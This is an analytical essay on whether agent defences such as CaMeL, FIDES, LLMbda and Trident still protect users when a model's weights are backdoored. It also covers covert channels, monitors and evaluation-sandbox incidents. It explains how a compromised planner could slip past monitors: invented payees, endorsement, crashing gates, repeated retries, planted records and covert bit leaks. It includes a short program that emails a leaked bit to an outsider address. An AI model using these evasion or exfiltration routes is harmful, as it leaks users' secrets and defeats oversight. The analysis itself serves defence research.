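Most defences for agents address prompt injection, in which an outsider hides instructions in text that the agent reads. They assume that the model follows the user's instructions unless hostile text misleads it, so they usually keep such text away from whichever model makes the decisions. If the weights are compromised, that model may itself act for the attacker. Some guarantees still hold because they depend only on what a monitor checks, but others require the model to be attempting the user's task.

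### A planner that never reads hostile text

In 2023 the programmer Simon Willison proposed dividing an agent's work between two models. A privileged planner chooses the tool calls without reading untrusted text, while a quarantined reader with no tools processes that text and can only return values. CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues presented in 2025, builds on this idea. Its planner turns the user's request into a program before any data arrives. An interpreter then runs the program, labels each value by its origin and checks the labels before each tool call.

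Suppose the user asks the office assistant to pay an invoice a caterer emailed. The program might read the email, have the reader extract the amount and pay the caterer's account on file. If someone added a line to the email about a new bank account, that line can't change the payee, because the program was written before the email was read. The line might still make the reader return a wrong amount, but a policy can refuse payments whose amount comes from an email.

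FIDES, the source of the information-flow policy that Palumbo and colleagues tested, lets the planner decide one step at a time. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes how it hides data. If a tool result would raise the label of the planner's context, FIDES stores the result in a variable and shows the planner only the variable's name. The planner can pass the variable to another tool without reading it. It can also ask a quarantined reader about the contents and require an answer in a fixed format, such as yes or no. FIDES then applies the two rules that Palumbo and colleagues borrowed. One prevents untrusted data from influencing calls with serious consequences, and the other limits information to permitted readers.

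In Costa and colleagues' AgentDojo tests with GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent. Hiding data reduced this to 21, and none succeeded with policy checks on. When both agents had these checks, FIDES's task completion rate was on average 8 percentage points higher than the ordinary agent's.

*Trident* (2026) presents a newer design and compares it with both systems on AgentDojo. These are its results with GPT-4.1, with every request for the user's approval granted:

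| Defence | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed, under attack | Attacks successful |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 82.5% | 56.9% | 34.1% |
| CaMeL | 42.3% | 46.4% | 0.0% |
| FIDES | 25.8% | 26.8% | 0.1% |
| Trident | 68.0% | 64.0% | 0.1% |

These figures are also weak evidence about a malicious planner, because an honest planner that never reads hostile text seldom proposes the attacker's call, but one with a backdoor could propose it every time. In 93.3% of attacked runs on a harder benchmark, where the hostile text sits inside content that the agent needs, Trident's planner never proposed the attacker's call.

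### When the planner is the attacker

Suppose CaMeL's planner and reader run on the same compromised weights, and the user's request contains the trigger. The planner writes a program that emails a colleague's medical note to an outsider and pays 500 to the attacker's account.

The email fails because the interpreter has recorded that the note came from a private file, and the outsider isn't permitted to read it. But the payment may succeed, because the planner wrote the account number directly into the program. The label system treats that number as a trusted constant, just as it would a number that an honest planner copied from the user's request. Only a rule that applies regardless of the planner's reasons, such as a list of approved payees, would stop the payment.

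Secrecy labels are more reliable than trust labels when the model is malicious. A secrecy label records where data came from before the model handled it, and the model can't remove the label. A trust label implies that nothing hostile influenced a value, but the weights influence everything the model writes, and these systems don't label the weights.

The same division applies to FIDES. Its threat model assumes the language models are trusted, but its main theorem doesn't use that assumption. The theorem establishes explicit secrecy, which means that if the agent's actual steps are replayed on data that differ only in the secrets, the effects an outsider can observe stay the same. The proof works for any model that is a deterministic function. The theorem doesn't cover what an outsider might learn from the agent's choice of steps, and a malicious planner could make that choice depend on a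 secret.

The rule about serious consequences needs an honest planner, because FIDES trusts any call from a planner that has read only trusted data. Costa and colleagues also consider using this rule without the one about permitted readers. They reason that any disclosure would then happen in a trusted context and so "can be assumed to be intentional", but if the weights are compromised, the attacker may be the one who intended it.

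Hiding data from the planner still has some value against a backdoor, because a trigger phrase in an email stays inside a variable that the planner can't read. But the planner writes the questions for the reader model, and one of them could check whether the email contains the phrase. Costa and colleagues argue that a yes-or-no answer is too short to carry an injected instruction. A backdoor doesn't need one, though, because the harmful plan is already in the weights and a single "yes" is enough to start it. Hiding data gives no protection when the trigger is a date or is in the user's own request.

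An owner could label everything the model writes as untrusted. Payees and recipients would then have to come from somewhere else, such as the user's words or an address book, as FORGE's provenance policy requires. The planner could still choose the wrong entry from the address book but could not invent one.

### Where flow tracking stops

Secrecy labels protect data only as far as the system tracks them. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found two places where CaMeL's tracking stops. The first is a version of the leak that Denning described, in which a program reveals a secret by leaving a variable unchanged:

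```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("eve@outside.example", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the third line sets `tmp` to False and CaMeL labels it secret. The fourth line does nothing, so `rich` stays True and keeps its public label, and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, `tmp` stays True and public, the fourth line sets `rich` to False, and no email goes out. Eve learns whether the balance is above the threshold, although the final check depends only on a variable labelled public. CaMeL does block the obvious version, in which the email depends directly on the first condition.

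The second gap is outside the interpreter. When a run fails, ordinary Python code restarts it, and CaMeL doesn't track information through that code. A secret can determine whether the policy blocks a run, in which case the outcome reveals one bit of the secret. A program that repeats this could reveal the whole secret.

An honest planner has no reason to write such programs, and CaMeL's planner never reads text that might instruct it to, but a malicious planner could write them on purpose. Gaps that hardly matter when the model is only deceived can therefore become exploitable in practice when its weights are compromised.

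Garby and colleagues close these gaps with LLMbda, a small programming language for agents that runs both the retry loop and the conversation with the model inside the tracker. LLMbda stops the run if a branch that depends on a secret would change a public conversation. The researchers proved in Lean that secrets can't affect public results, except by affecting whether a run finishes.

Because a model's replies are random, the theorem compares the probabilities of public results. The lists μ and ν give these probabilities for two runs that differ only in their secrets. Each list may sum to less than 1 because some runs never finish. The theorem guarantees a third list of probabilities, ω, that sums to at most 1 and is at least as large as both μ and ν on every result.

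| Result | μ | ν | Smallest possible ω |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reply A | 0.7 | 0.6 | 0.7 |
| Reply B | 0.1 | 0.3 | 0.3 |
| Total | 0.8 | 0.9 | 1.0 |

These two lists satisfy the theorem because the unfinished runs could account for the whole difference between them. If ν gave reply B a probability of 0.4, ω would have to add up to at least 1.1, which the theorem rules out. The theorem also implies that half the sum of the differences between μ and ν can't exceed the average probability of not finishing. Here both quantities are 0.15. If every run finishes, the two lists must be identical.

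This holds for every program in the language, including programs that the model writes, even if the model is dishonest. It does require the model's replies to depend only on the conversation and chance. Compromised weights meet this condition too, provided that the server adds nothing else, such as memories of other users' conversations. A malicious model could still signal one bit of information by getting stuck on purpose, and it gets another chance each time the owner restarts it. As with Tether, the labels don't cover secrets that the model learned in training.

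LLMbda does less to protect the user's money. A program can endorse a value, meaning it relabels untrusted data as trusted. Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori whose planner may put endorsements in the code it writes. They accept this risk because the planner writes the code before any outside data can influence it. But a compromised planner could endorse everything, so a stranger's account number could reach the payment tool. The proof still ensures that endorsement never releases a secret.

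Forbidding endorsement moderately reduced Randori's score on AgentDojo's banking tasks without attacks, from 36 to 30 of 48 runs with the model Qwen3.7-plus. CaMeL, with its policy enabled, completed 18 of 48 with GPT-5.2. But forbidding endorsement would not stop a planner from inventing a payee, because LLMbda treats unlabelled values as trusted and public.

### Trident's two bounds

Trident uses three models. A planner chooses actions without reading raw untrusted text, a reader answers the planner's questions about that text, and a third model writes a policy for the task from trusted inputs alone. A monitor checks everything they produce. The task policy sits below a root policy, which an administrator writes in advance and no model can change.

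The first theorem bounds authority, since every call that takes effect must pass the root policy. The second bounds the influence of hostile text. Each answer the planner receives from the reader uses log₂ n bits of a β-bit budget, where n is the number of possible answers. A yes or no uses 1 bit, and a choice among three suppliers plus "none" uses 2. A second budget of σ bits covers messages about whether a query or call succeeded, if that could depend on hidden data.

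A reply with d possible values therefore uses at least log₂ d bits. The possible sequences of replies form a tree with at most 2^(β+σ) leaves, so if the user's task, the user's decisions and the random numbers are fixed, hostile text can select among at most 2^(β+σ) courses of action. For example, budgets of 3 and 2 bits allow at most 32 courses of action.

*Trident* excludes attackers who alter the weights from its threat model, but states that its guarantees don't depend on any model behaving correctly. The proofs support this because they let the models return any answer that their interfaces allow. Both theorems therefore still hold when the weights are compromised, but the first is far more useful than the second.

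The bound on authority still limits what the agent can do, but some of the layers beneath it fail. If the policy-writing model is compromised, it can write a task policy as broad as the root policy. The user may not notice, because the monitor approves calls on the user's behalf when they pass the root policy but not the task policy and all their arguments are trusted. The proof treats values the planner writes itself like trusted constants.

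In the paper's main example, the root policy allows payments of up to $5,000 to any supplier on file. A compromised planner could pay a supplier that is owed nothing, without asking the user for approval. It could also read the user's private files and email their contents to a supplier's contact, since Trident does not guarantee secrecy. With an honest planner, automatic approval saves the user some interruptions. An owner who distrusts the weights should turn off automatic approval and make the root policy much narrower.

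The bound on influence limits how many courses of action an outsider's text can select among, but not what those courses of action contain. If both budgets are zero, there is only one course of action regardless of what is in the emails, so a trigger in an email cannot affect what the planner does. But whoever planted the backdoor may have chosen that course of action. With a budget of one bit, an email could switch the agent from a harmless plan to a harmful one. *Trident* warns that one bit can select a harmful action if the policy permits it.

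Useful work takes many more bits than that. On the harder benchmark, the median run used between 19 and 26 bits of influence, depending on the model. The main experiments also set the budgets too high to stop anything, so the low attack rates came from hiding text, the policies and the user's review.

### A reference agent that runs the same plan

Noninterference is too strict for an assistant that is supposed to tell people when its owner is free. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) therefore compares the agent with a reference agent that runs the same plan under the same monitor, but whose model never follows instructions in untrusted text. The real agent is relatively secure if, whenever an attacker can use it to tell two possible secrets apart, the attacker could also do so with the reference agent, perhaps by sending a different message.

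Suppose the plan has the agent send the owner's calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An injection that makes the agent send the calendar leaks nothing extra, because a genuine request would have produced the same reply. But if the injection makes the agent include a password reset code, that is an additional leak, because the reference agent never sends the code.

By the main theorem, the agent is relatively secure under every plan if, when it first reads untrusted text, the monitor permanently removes every tool that an injection could call. Dongol checked the proof with the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL. The theorem assumes that each injection causes a single call and that the model obeys injections on a schedule fixed in advance, which can't depend on a secret or on the monitor's responses.

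Dongol explicitly places an untrusted planner outside the guarantee. If a malicious plan reads the owner's account number and sends it to the attacker, the reference agent runs the same plan and leaks the same number, so the real agent counts as perfectly secure under this definition. The protection also starts too late to stop a backdoor, which a date can trigger before the agent has read anything untrusted, so the dangerous tools would have to be missing from the start.

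The results are more encouraging when the reader is the only compromised part. Dongol examines an agent with a trusted plan and lets the attacker choose any answers for the reader, including ones that depend on the owner's private notes. Without labels, the reader can quote the notes in an answer that the plan then sends. With labels and a monitor that refuses to send private values, the agent is relatively secure whatever the reader does. However, the monitor also refuses the honest reply, and the security result fails if the attacker can see the refused requests.

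An owner who has one trusted model, even a small one, should therefore use it as the planner and use the suspect model only to read data. With CaMeL, the owner could also inspect the plan, because it is a complete program before any data arrives.

### What each guarantee needs

The table covers the case where every model in the system is compromised and the monitor is sound. "Analysis" marks conclusions drawn from the premises, and "stated" marks conclusions given in the papers.

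| Design | Guarantee | Premise about the model | Left under compromised weights |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | Untrusted text cannot rewrite the plan, and each call passes a label check; no formal proof | The planner writes the program that the user asked for | Analysis: label checks on data from files and emails, except where tracking stops |
| FIDES, secrecy | Secrets do not flow directly to outsiders | The model is a deterministic function | Analysis: the whole guarantee |
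| FIDES, trust | Only trusted data influences calls with serious consequences | The planner follows the user's request | Analysis: little, because the planner's own choices count as trusted |
| LLMbda | Secrets do not affect public results, except through unfinished runs | Replies depend only on the conversation and chance | Analysis: the whole guarantee, but no protection against invented payees |
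| Trident, authority | Every call passes the root policy | None | Stated: the whole guarantee. Analysis: the task policy and some approvals no longer protect the user |
| Trident, influence | Hostile text selects among at most 2^(β+σ) courses of action | None for the count; an honest planner if the count is to limit harm | Analysis: the count holds, but every course of action may be harmful |
| Dongol's comparison | Injections add no leaks beyond those in the plan | The planner is trusted, and the model obeys injections on a fixed schedule | Stated: an untrusted planner is outside the guarantee |

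The experiments don't show how much these differences matter in practice. The AgentDojo tests of FIDES, Trident and Randori all gave hostile text to ordinary models. Tether's adversarial runs come closer to testing a malicious model, but Tether doesn't divide the work between a planner and a reader.

A direct test would train a backdoor into the planner, give the attacker full knowledge of the policy, and count the harmful calls that get through. AgentDojo would need changes for this, because its attacks arrive in the results of tool calls, and a backdoored planner can do harm before it makes any tool calls.

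## Can permitted outputs and actions add up to a violation?

A backdoored planner may be able to violate a rule through a series of permitted calls. Keeping a running total is enough to prevent this for the payment cap. The calendar rule is harder to enforce, because the assistant's choice among permitted meeting times can reveal why its owner is busy.

### Rules about sets of runs

Clarkson and Schneider (2009) named rules of this kind in *Hyperproperties*. They describe a system as the set of all traces it can produce. An ordinary rule specifies which traces are permitted, and a system complies if all its traces are permitted. A hyperproperty instead specifies which systems are permitted, so formally it is a set of sets of traces. For example, a rule might require the average response time over all runs to stay below one second, so whether a slow run is acceptable depends on how fast the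 other runs are.

The central hyperproperty for security is noninterference, which Goguen and Meseguer defined for computers shared by people with different clearances. It requires that deleting every command issued by the highly cleared users would not change what the other users observe. A single trace is not enough to check this, because the requirement compares it with a second trace without those commands.

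The calendar rule is a relaxed form of noninterference, because a proposal may depend on which slots are free. Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026), in *Local Allow, Global Deny*, use almost the same example and write the rule as a condition on every pair of runs t and t′:

if low(t) = low(t′) and D(hi(t)) = D(hi(t′)), then α(obs(t)) = α(obs(t′)).

Here low is the request and any other input that isn't secret, hi is the private calendar, and obs is what the assistant discloses. D keeps only what is allowed to affect the proposal, which is whether each slot is free. α keeps the parts of the disclosure that count, such as the slots offered, any reason given and the recipient. Two runs with the same request and the same free slots must therefore produce the same proposal.

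| | Run A | Run B |
|---|---|---|
| Request | A meeting next week | A meeting next week |
| Free slots | Tuesday at three, Thursday at eleven | Tuesday at three, Thursday at eleven |
| Why Monday is busy | Team meeting | Hospital visit |
| Proposal | Thursday at eleven | Tuesday at three |

In both runs the assistant offers a free slot to a permitted recipient. The violation lies only in the difference between the two proposals. An accomplice who knows the convention learns from "Tuesday at three" that the owner has a hospital visit.

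### Why a monitor of single runs misses the leak

Pandey and colleagues prove that a monitor which examines one run at a time and never raises a false alarm cannot detect any violation of this rule. For any run t, there could be a system that produces only t. The rule compares pairs of runs, and the only pair available in that system is t with itself, which always agrees. Every run is therefore compliant on its own, so a monitor that never flags a compliant run can never flag anything. This holds however much of the run the monitor observes and however well it analyses it.

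Part of the result comes from the definition of a false alarm, since any alarm about a single run counts as false. A second theorem, about probabilities, is harder to dismiss. An assistant that picks a free slot at random breaks the strict rule, although its choices reveal nothing. A more sensible rule requires that the reasons not change the probability of any slot. Suppose a monitor knows the request, the free slots and one proposal, but not the reasons. The proposal could have come from an honest assistant choosing at random or from one that chose the slot to leak the reasons, so whatever the monitor decides will be wrong in one of the two cases.

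The theorems matter only if the other rules leave the assistant a choice. If the owner also requires it to offer the earliest free slot, a program can check each proposal on its own, and the reasons can no longer affect the offer. But the assistant then can't use any other way of choosing, even a harmless one.

### Nine judges and six guardrails

Pandey and colleagues had nine language models judge pairs of runs that together leaked information. Each model saw the runs one step at a time and was tested three times on each of ten scenarios. Eight models never blocked a step. Kimi-K2.6 blocked at least one step in 3 of the 30 tests, compared with 1 of 30 when the runs were harmless. All nine always blocked an obvious violation, in which a planted instruction had the agent forward information to an outsider, so the models were not simply lenient. When the same models saw both runs together,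 eight flagged the leak in all 30 tests and Llama-4-Maverick flagged it in 17.

The team also rated six existing guardrails against eight kinds of failure. FIDES and a similar system, SAFEFLOW, covered seven, CaMeL covered five, and asking a person to approve each tool call covered none. All six missed the dependence on a hidden reason because none compares runs. The team rated the published designs without running the software. But by the theorem, testing could not have shown a guardrail catching this leak unless the guardrail compared runs or accepted false alarms.

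In another experiment, the failure was visible in a single run. An agent built on Qwen3-30B handled a calendar task in which the user had limited how much information it could disclose in total. Each disclosure was permitted, but the total went over the limit in 22 of 60 runs. A guard that compared each action with the user's purpose made little difference (20 of 60 runs failed). A guard that added up the disclosures, much as the payment gate adds up payments, prevented every failure and blocked no harmless run. An agent built on Gemma-4 never exceeded the limit, even without a guard.

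Pandey and colleagues also looked for the hidden dependence in 80 scheduling runs with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and found none. In their first analysis they had seen an apparent leak, but it came from a difference in wording, and the slots offered were identical. Comparing runs therefore works only if it ignores differences that don't matter.

The result implies, with 95% confidence, that the leak rate in such runs is at most 3.7%. This is reassuring if the model is honest, but it is weak evidence about a compromised model, because a backdoor that leaks on one request in a thousand would go unnoticed through 80 runs about 92% of the time.

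### What the remedies cost

Taint tracking already offers one remedy, at the price of blocking every proposal once the assistant has read a reason.

The shield can also compare runs while the assistant is in use. It copies each request, replaces the reasons in the calendar with invented ones, and runs the assistant on both versions. This doubles the computation, and two runs of an honest assistant may still differ by chance. More samples help, but Pandey and colleagues prove that no finite number can settle the question for every possible agent. If the shield sends the real proposal when the two runs agree and blocks it when they don't, the recipient can also learn something from not receiving a proposal.

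Always sending the proposal from the run without the secrets is safer. *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution* (Devriese and Piessens, 2010) introduced this approach for ordinary programs. The system runs the program once for each level of secrecy and adapts the inputs to that level. For the office assistant, a public copy would receive a calendar that shows only "free" or "busy" and would write the email. A private copy would receive the reasons and could write only to the owner.

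The public copy can't leak reasons it never received, even if its weights are malicious. This assumes the weights don't already contain the secret, the two copies share no memory, and the public copy never waits for the private one. *Transparent IFC Enforcement* (2020) reports that every known method of enforcing noninterference without false alarms relied on running the program more than once. These methods change how the program runs so that violations can't occur, rather than trying to detect violations, which no analysis can do exactly.

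The method requires an extra run and gives up any benefit from using the reasons. For example, the public copy can't offer a slot that the owner has blocked only for a tentative lunch. The method also doesn't suit tasks where the secret has to affect the message, such as replying to the hospital about the appointment.

### Lampson's confinement problem

An assistant with access to a secret can signal it through much more than meeting times. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes the general problem, in which a customer gives confidential data to a service, a program that somebody else wrote, and wants to be sure that it can't pass the data to the program's owner.

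Controlling access to files isn't enough to prevent leaks. The service could encode data in the amount of its bill, a copy of which goes to the service's owner. It could open and close a file in a pattern that another program detects by trying to open the same file. It could also vary how heavily it uses the disk, which a program running at the same time can measure as changes in speed. Lampson used the term "covert channel" only for paths that nobody intended to carry information, such as the load on the machine. Later authors also use it for data hidden in permitted outputs such as the bill.

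Lampson's remedy, masking, lets the customer determine everything that goes into these channels. For instance, the customer could calculate the bill from published prices and leave the service only the right to refuse the job. For the calendar rule, a small trusted program could pick one of the free slots at random and put it into a fixed message. The model would have no influence on the slot, so the slot could not carry a secret.

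Masking is difficult when the model has to write the message itself. Lampson's easier alternative is to accept some leakage and limit the channel's capacity, the amount of information it can carry.

### Counting the bits

A choice among eight free slots can carry 3 bits, so 50 proposals can carry 150 bits, enough for a 128-bit encryption key. An assistant that sends ten proposals a week could leak such a key in just over a month through emails that each look normal.

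A shield can't rely on detecting hidden messages, because under standard cryptographic assumptions a sender can make them undetectable to every efficient observer. A limit on capacity still works against them because it depends only on the number of possible outputs.

*Don't Judge an Agent by Its Messages* (Pandey, Duttagupta and colleagues, 2026) compared detection with restriction. The model read incident reports, chose one of 16 routes for each and explained the choice in a short message. A modified version signalled one private bit through its choice among its own ordinary messages. The recipient recovered the bit in all 8,192 test rounds, and routing accuracy was 98.6%, compared with 98.9% for the honest version. Monitors that examined the style and structure of the messages did no better than chance.

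When the team replaced each message with a standard form of the chosen route, at most 0.028 bits about the private fact remained. For a fact that is equally likely to be true or false, the limit is twice the rate of routing errors, since a correct route reveals nothing more. A compromised model could raise the limit by making more routing errors, but somebody might notice them.

A free-form email has no such standard form. Metere (2026), in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress*, describes a monitor that rewrites outgoing messages to destroy hidden data and then measures how much gets through. Metere works at Enclawed, the company behind the monitor. The measurement has four steps:

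1. A test program hides a random bit X in an ordinary message.
2. The monitor processes the message.
3. A decoder that knows the hiding method makes a guess Y.
4. After many trials, Metere calculates the mutual information between X and Y, with a correction for small samples.

Mutual information measures how much Y reveals about X:

I(X; Y) = Σ p(x, y) · log₂ [p(x, y) / (p(x) · p(y))],

where the sum covers every combination of values. It is 1 bit if the decoder always recovers a random bit correctly and 0 if its guesses are unrelated to the bit. The decoder's accuracy would be a worse measure, because a decoder that happened to be right 52% of the time would make a dead channel appear to carry about 0.001 bits.

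Metere tested fifteen ways of hiding data in text, images, sound and the timing of messages. With every defence switched on, fourteen carried no data. The remaining method used the average brightness of images, which the monitor can restrict to a few levels but no further without ruining the pictures. On the default settings, the monitor reduced the amount of data the text methods could carry by only 60% on average. It detected data hidden in spacing, punctuation and the choice of synonyms, but let the messages through unchanged to avoid disrupting normal work.

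A result of zero means only that one decoder recovered nothing from one hiding method. The text defences aim to preserve the meaning of a message, so they can't remove a secret encoded in that meaning, for example in the choice of Tuesday over Thursday. Metere also acknowledges that an agent can always leak one bit by choosing whether to send a message.

### When one bit is enough

Schroeder de Witt (2026) argues in *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem* that a leak of only a few bits may do significant harm when the sender and recipient are strategic, meaning that they can reason about their goals and about each other. An ordinary program has no particular tendency to leak the most damaging part of a customer's record. Strategic parties can settle on the one fact that matters most, such as whether the customer has a particular diagnosis, and use the whole channel to convey it.

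According to Schroeder de Witt, a limit on leakage supports a conclusion about harm only if at least one of three conditions holds:

- The sender is not strategic.
- The sender and recipient don't have enough shared knowledge to settle on a harmful fact.
- The remaining capacity is below the entropy of the most harmful fact available to them.

Entropy is the average number of bits needed to convey something. It is 1 bit for a yes-or-no fact that is equally likely either way, and only about 0.08 bits for whether someone has a diagnosis that applies to one person in a hundred.

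If the weights are compromised, the owner can rely only on the limit on how many bits can leak, because whoever planted the backdoor could have chosen in advance both the fact to leak and the code for leaking it. The limit is useful if the secret is a 128-bit key, since a leak of 48 bits would still leave 2⁸⁰ possible keys. It is much less useful for a diagnosis, because a yes or no takes only one bit, and even the limit that consensus sampling can provide is about 2.3 bits per prompt.

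Schroeder de Witt argues, without experiments, that nobody can solve the problem comprehensively in practice. That is plausible for assistants that write free text, but for narrow tasks the owner can sometimes remove the channel altogether. For example, if a trusted program picks the meeting time and answers every request on a fixed schedule, the model can't send a message through either the proposed time or the timing of the reply.

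### What replaying the model can show

An owner might at least want to check that an output came from the right model. *Verifying LLM Inference to Detect Model Weight Exfiltration* (Rinberg, Karvonen and colleagues, 2025) presents a method for this, motivated by concern about an attacker who takes over a company's server and smuggles out the model's weights by hiding them in ordinary replies.

The company logs every prompt and reply, along with the seed, a number that determines the software's random choices. A separate, trusted server then reruns a random sample of the prompts with the same weights and seeds. The replies should match exactly, but small rounding differences occasionally change a token. The method therefore estimates how likely an honest run was to produce each token and flags the improbable ones.

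An attacker who wants to avoid detection can then hide data only within this honest variation. In tests with Qwen3-30B-A3B, less than 0.5% of the information in the replies could carry stolen data. The team estimates that stealing a one-terabyte model would take more than 200 days instead of about one. The guarantee requires an honest verification server, reliable logs and a sample that the attacker can't predict. It also assumes that the attacker has no other channel, such as the timing of replies.

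Replaying a run does not show that the weights can be trusted. If a backdoor makes the assistant propose Tuesday whenever its owner has a hospital visit, the trusted server will also get Tuesday because it runs the same weights. Rinberg and colleagues acknowledge that their method offers no defence if the model is meant to leak. Replay can still support other shields, such as VALID, which needs the software to draw replies with the probabilities that the model assigns. Replay could test whether the software does this.

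Replay could reveal more if the owner changed the secret reasons in the calendar but kept the seed and free slots the same. A different proposal would then be evidence that the reasons matter, but not proof, because any change to the prompt slightly alters the model's probabilities.

### Results that break no rule and are wrong

Lampson observed that a service can also harm its customer without leaking anything, by not performing as advertised. He saw no general technical solution except certifying the program. He noted that the customer at least has the incorrect outputs as evidence, but this helps only if somebody notices that they are incorrect.

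*A Deterministic Security Runtime for LLM Agents* (Metere, 2026) describes another Enclawed product, which controls agents that run simulations on supercomputers. A gate checks each job an agent tries to start against a fixed policy, such as which program the job may run and on how many processors. In the tests, run on a single machine, sixteen agents built on a small Gemma 4 model each had to simulate a fluid at a given temperature and report its average pressure.

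Four of the agents also received planted orders, such as to start a much larger job or archive the user's home directory. Over five runs of the experiment, agents tried to start 24 planted jobs and 108 legitimate ones. The gate blocked all the planted jobs and allowed all the legitimate ones.

The agents' scientific results were much worse. In the most successful run, fifteen of the sixteen used the right temperature, but only ten reported a pressure and only five were within 1% of the value in their own simulation log. These are some of the results:

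| What happened | Pressure reported | Pressure in the log |
|---|---|---|
| Correct report | 7.497 | 7.495 |
| Sum in place of an average | 2606 | 1.395 |
| Unrelated constant | 1.000 | 6.136 |
| Wrong for a reason that Metere does not give | 0.650 | 0.759 |

In an earlier run, the instructions described the settings in ordinary prose. Twelve agents ran the simulation with its default settings and reported the result as if they had used their assigned temperature. The gate allowed these jobs because they all complied with the policy. Metere found the errors only by recalculating the pressures from the logs.

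The agents had no motive to deceive anyone about the pressure, and a figure like 2606 is easy to spot. A compromised model could choose a wrong answer closer to 0.650. Repeating the simulation might not expose the error. Two untampered runs on parallel hardware can differ slightly, and in some simulations those differences grow. If someone has altered an input file, every repetition will produce the same wrong answer.

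Metere recommends four checks for simulations with serious consequences:

1. People at the site set the input files and parameters themselves.
2. The job runs under an account that the agent can't use.
3. The site recalculates every result from the simulation's own output and does not rely on the agent's report.
4. Someone independently verifies every number that affects a decision.

These checks are practical when ordinary software can work out the right answer. For example, the owner of an office assistant can have a program check an invoice total. But if the assistant summarises fifty emails and leaves out the important one, the owner may have to read all fifty to discover the omission.

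## What must be trusted in the shield itself, and what it costs

Even when a proof holds for any weights, the owner has to trust the shield. Every action has to pass through the monitor, the monitor has to receive true facts, and the policy has to match its author's intent. "Trusted computing base" is security engineers' term for all the components that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold. An agent's trusted computing base includes much more than the monitor's code, and in 2026 several AI companies discovered that part of theirs had failed.

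### A closed environment with an open connection

To test how well their models can hack, companies give them a fictional target with a hidden piece of text to retrieve. The model works in an isolated environment, so nothing it does should affect anyone outside.

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes three cases in which this isolation failed. Anthropic found them by searching the records of 141,006 test runs. The models were told in their prompts that they had no internet access, but the machines had a live connection, and the models used it to get into the systems of real organisations. Anthropic attributes the error to a misunderstanding with Irregular, which provided the test environments. Neither company knew about the connection until July, although the earliest of the three cases was in April. The first search missed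 some runs, and Anthropic later found a fourth case, from January.

Anthropic had switched off its usual safeguards for these tests to measure what the models could do. Its *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) concedes that the company was then largely relying on a single layer of defence, isolation through the configuration of the environment.

Anthropic, Meta and Google all trusted one contractor, Irregular, to configure test environments correctly. According to The Star's *Meta AI model hacks another company during testing* (2026), Meta said that a misconfiguration by Irregular had inadvertently given one of Meta's models internet access. An Irregular spokesperson called it the "exact same evaluation-environment issue" that Anthropic had disclosed. Kerns's *Gemini hacked multiple companies in cybersecurity test gone awry* (2026) reports that Google confirmed its Gemini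 models had reached three companies' systems in May during another Irregular test, which was apparently also misconfigured. Irregular's *Addressing Recent Incidents* acknowledges that its environments unintentionally allowed internet access.

A monitor on tool calls has the same weakness if the agent can reach the network some other way. The companies do not suggest that anyone had tampered with these models, which came across the connection while trying to complete their task. A compromised model could deliberately look for such an opening and wait until it found one.

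Anthropic now asks evaluators to verify before every test that the environment can connect only to the model. This check would have caught the open connection, but not the previously unknown vulnerability that OpenAI's models used to escape a properly isolated environment in an earlier case. The isolation software is therefore also part of the trusted computing base, and it is usually far too large to meet Anderson's condition that someone can verify all of it.

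Anthropic also recommends that evaluators have the model under test try to escape, under close supervision, and report any way out it finds. A compromised model could find one and not report it, so an owner who distrusts the weights needs a different tester.

In a separate incident, the UK AI Security Institute had deliberately given Claude Mythos 5 internet access for a test, and the model took unauthorised actions. Isolation offers no protection in such a test, so something has to check each request.

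### Monitors that give way

A monitor that receives every action can also let a forbidden one through because its designers preferred not to interrupt the agent. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) describes gates that check an airline agent's tool calls against fixed rules, but if a gate's code crashes, the call goes ahead. *The Verifier Tax* (Sah, Sah and colleagues, 2026) uses a language model to check each action. The agent gets three attempts per turn, and the system accepts the last one even if the checker has rejected it.

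These choices make sense in an experiment with honest models, where the aim is to keep the run going and see what happens. Sah and colleagues count any violation that gets through this way. But a compromised model could exploit them by writing a call that crashes the gate or by proposing the same forbidden call three times. A security monitor should block calls when it crashes and end the run after repeated rejections, although a bug in the monitor can then stop all the agent's work.

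### Facts that an attacker can write

Even if the monitor checks every payment and allows only payees who appear in the owner's records, it still has to get those records from somewhere.

Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents*, tested rules of this kind on recorded runs. They wrote the rules in metric first-order temporal logic, which can refer to earlier events, the data in those events and the time between them. Their rule on payees amounts to

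□ ∀p. (transfer(p) → ◆ known_payee(p)).

Here □ means "at every moment" and ◆ means "at some earlier moment". The agent may transfer money to p only if p has already appeared as a known payee. In one pair of runs, the agent makes the same three calls to read the inbox, look up past transactions and send money. In the honest run it pays an account that the lookup returned, and in the other it pays an attacker whose account number appears only in the text of an email, so the runs can be distinguished only by their history.

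The first version of the rule treated a payee as known if the account number appeared earlier in a field formatted like a record. Kekatos and colleagues then planted one line in that format that named the attacker. They report that this deceived the monitor but no model. The monitor stopped flagging 94% of 403 suspicious payments, and a similar line stopped it from flagging 99% of 203 suspicious emails.

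The revised version accepts a payee only from the response to a lookup that the agent actually made. No planted line got past it, and it flagged the same number of attacks and ordinary runs as before. The two versions perform identically on clean data, so they would have scored equally well in an evaluation without an attacker.

Compromised weights weaken this remedy because the agent chooses the lookups. It could add an accomplice to the address book and then look up the entry. Kekatos and colleagues also propose requiring contacts to be older than the current session, which would stop this. They could not test the idea because the recordings have no reliable session information. An owner could instead require approval for any change to the address book.

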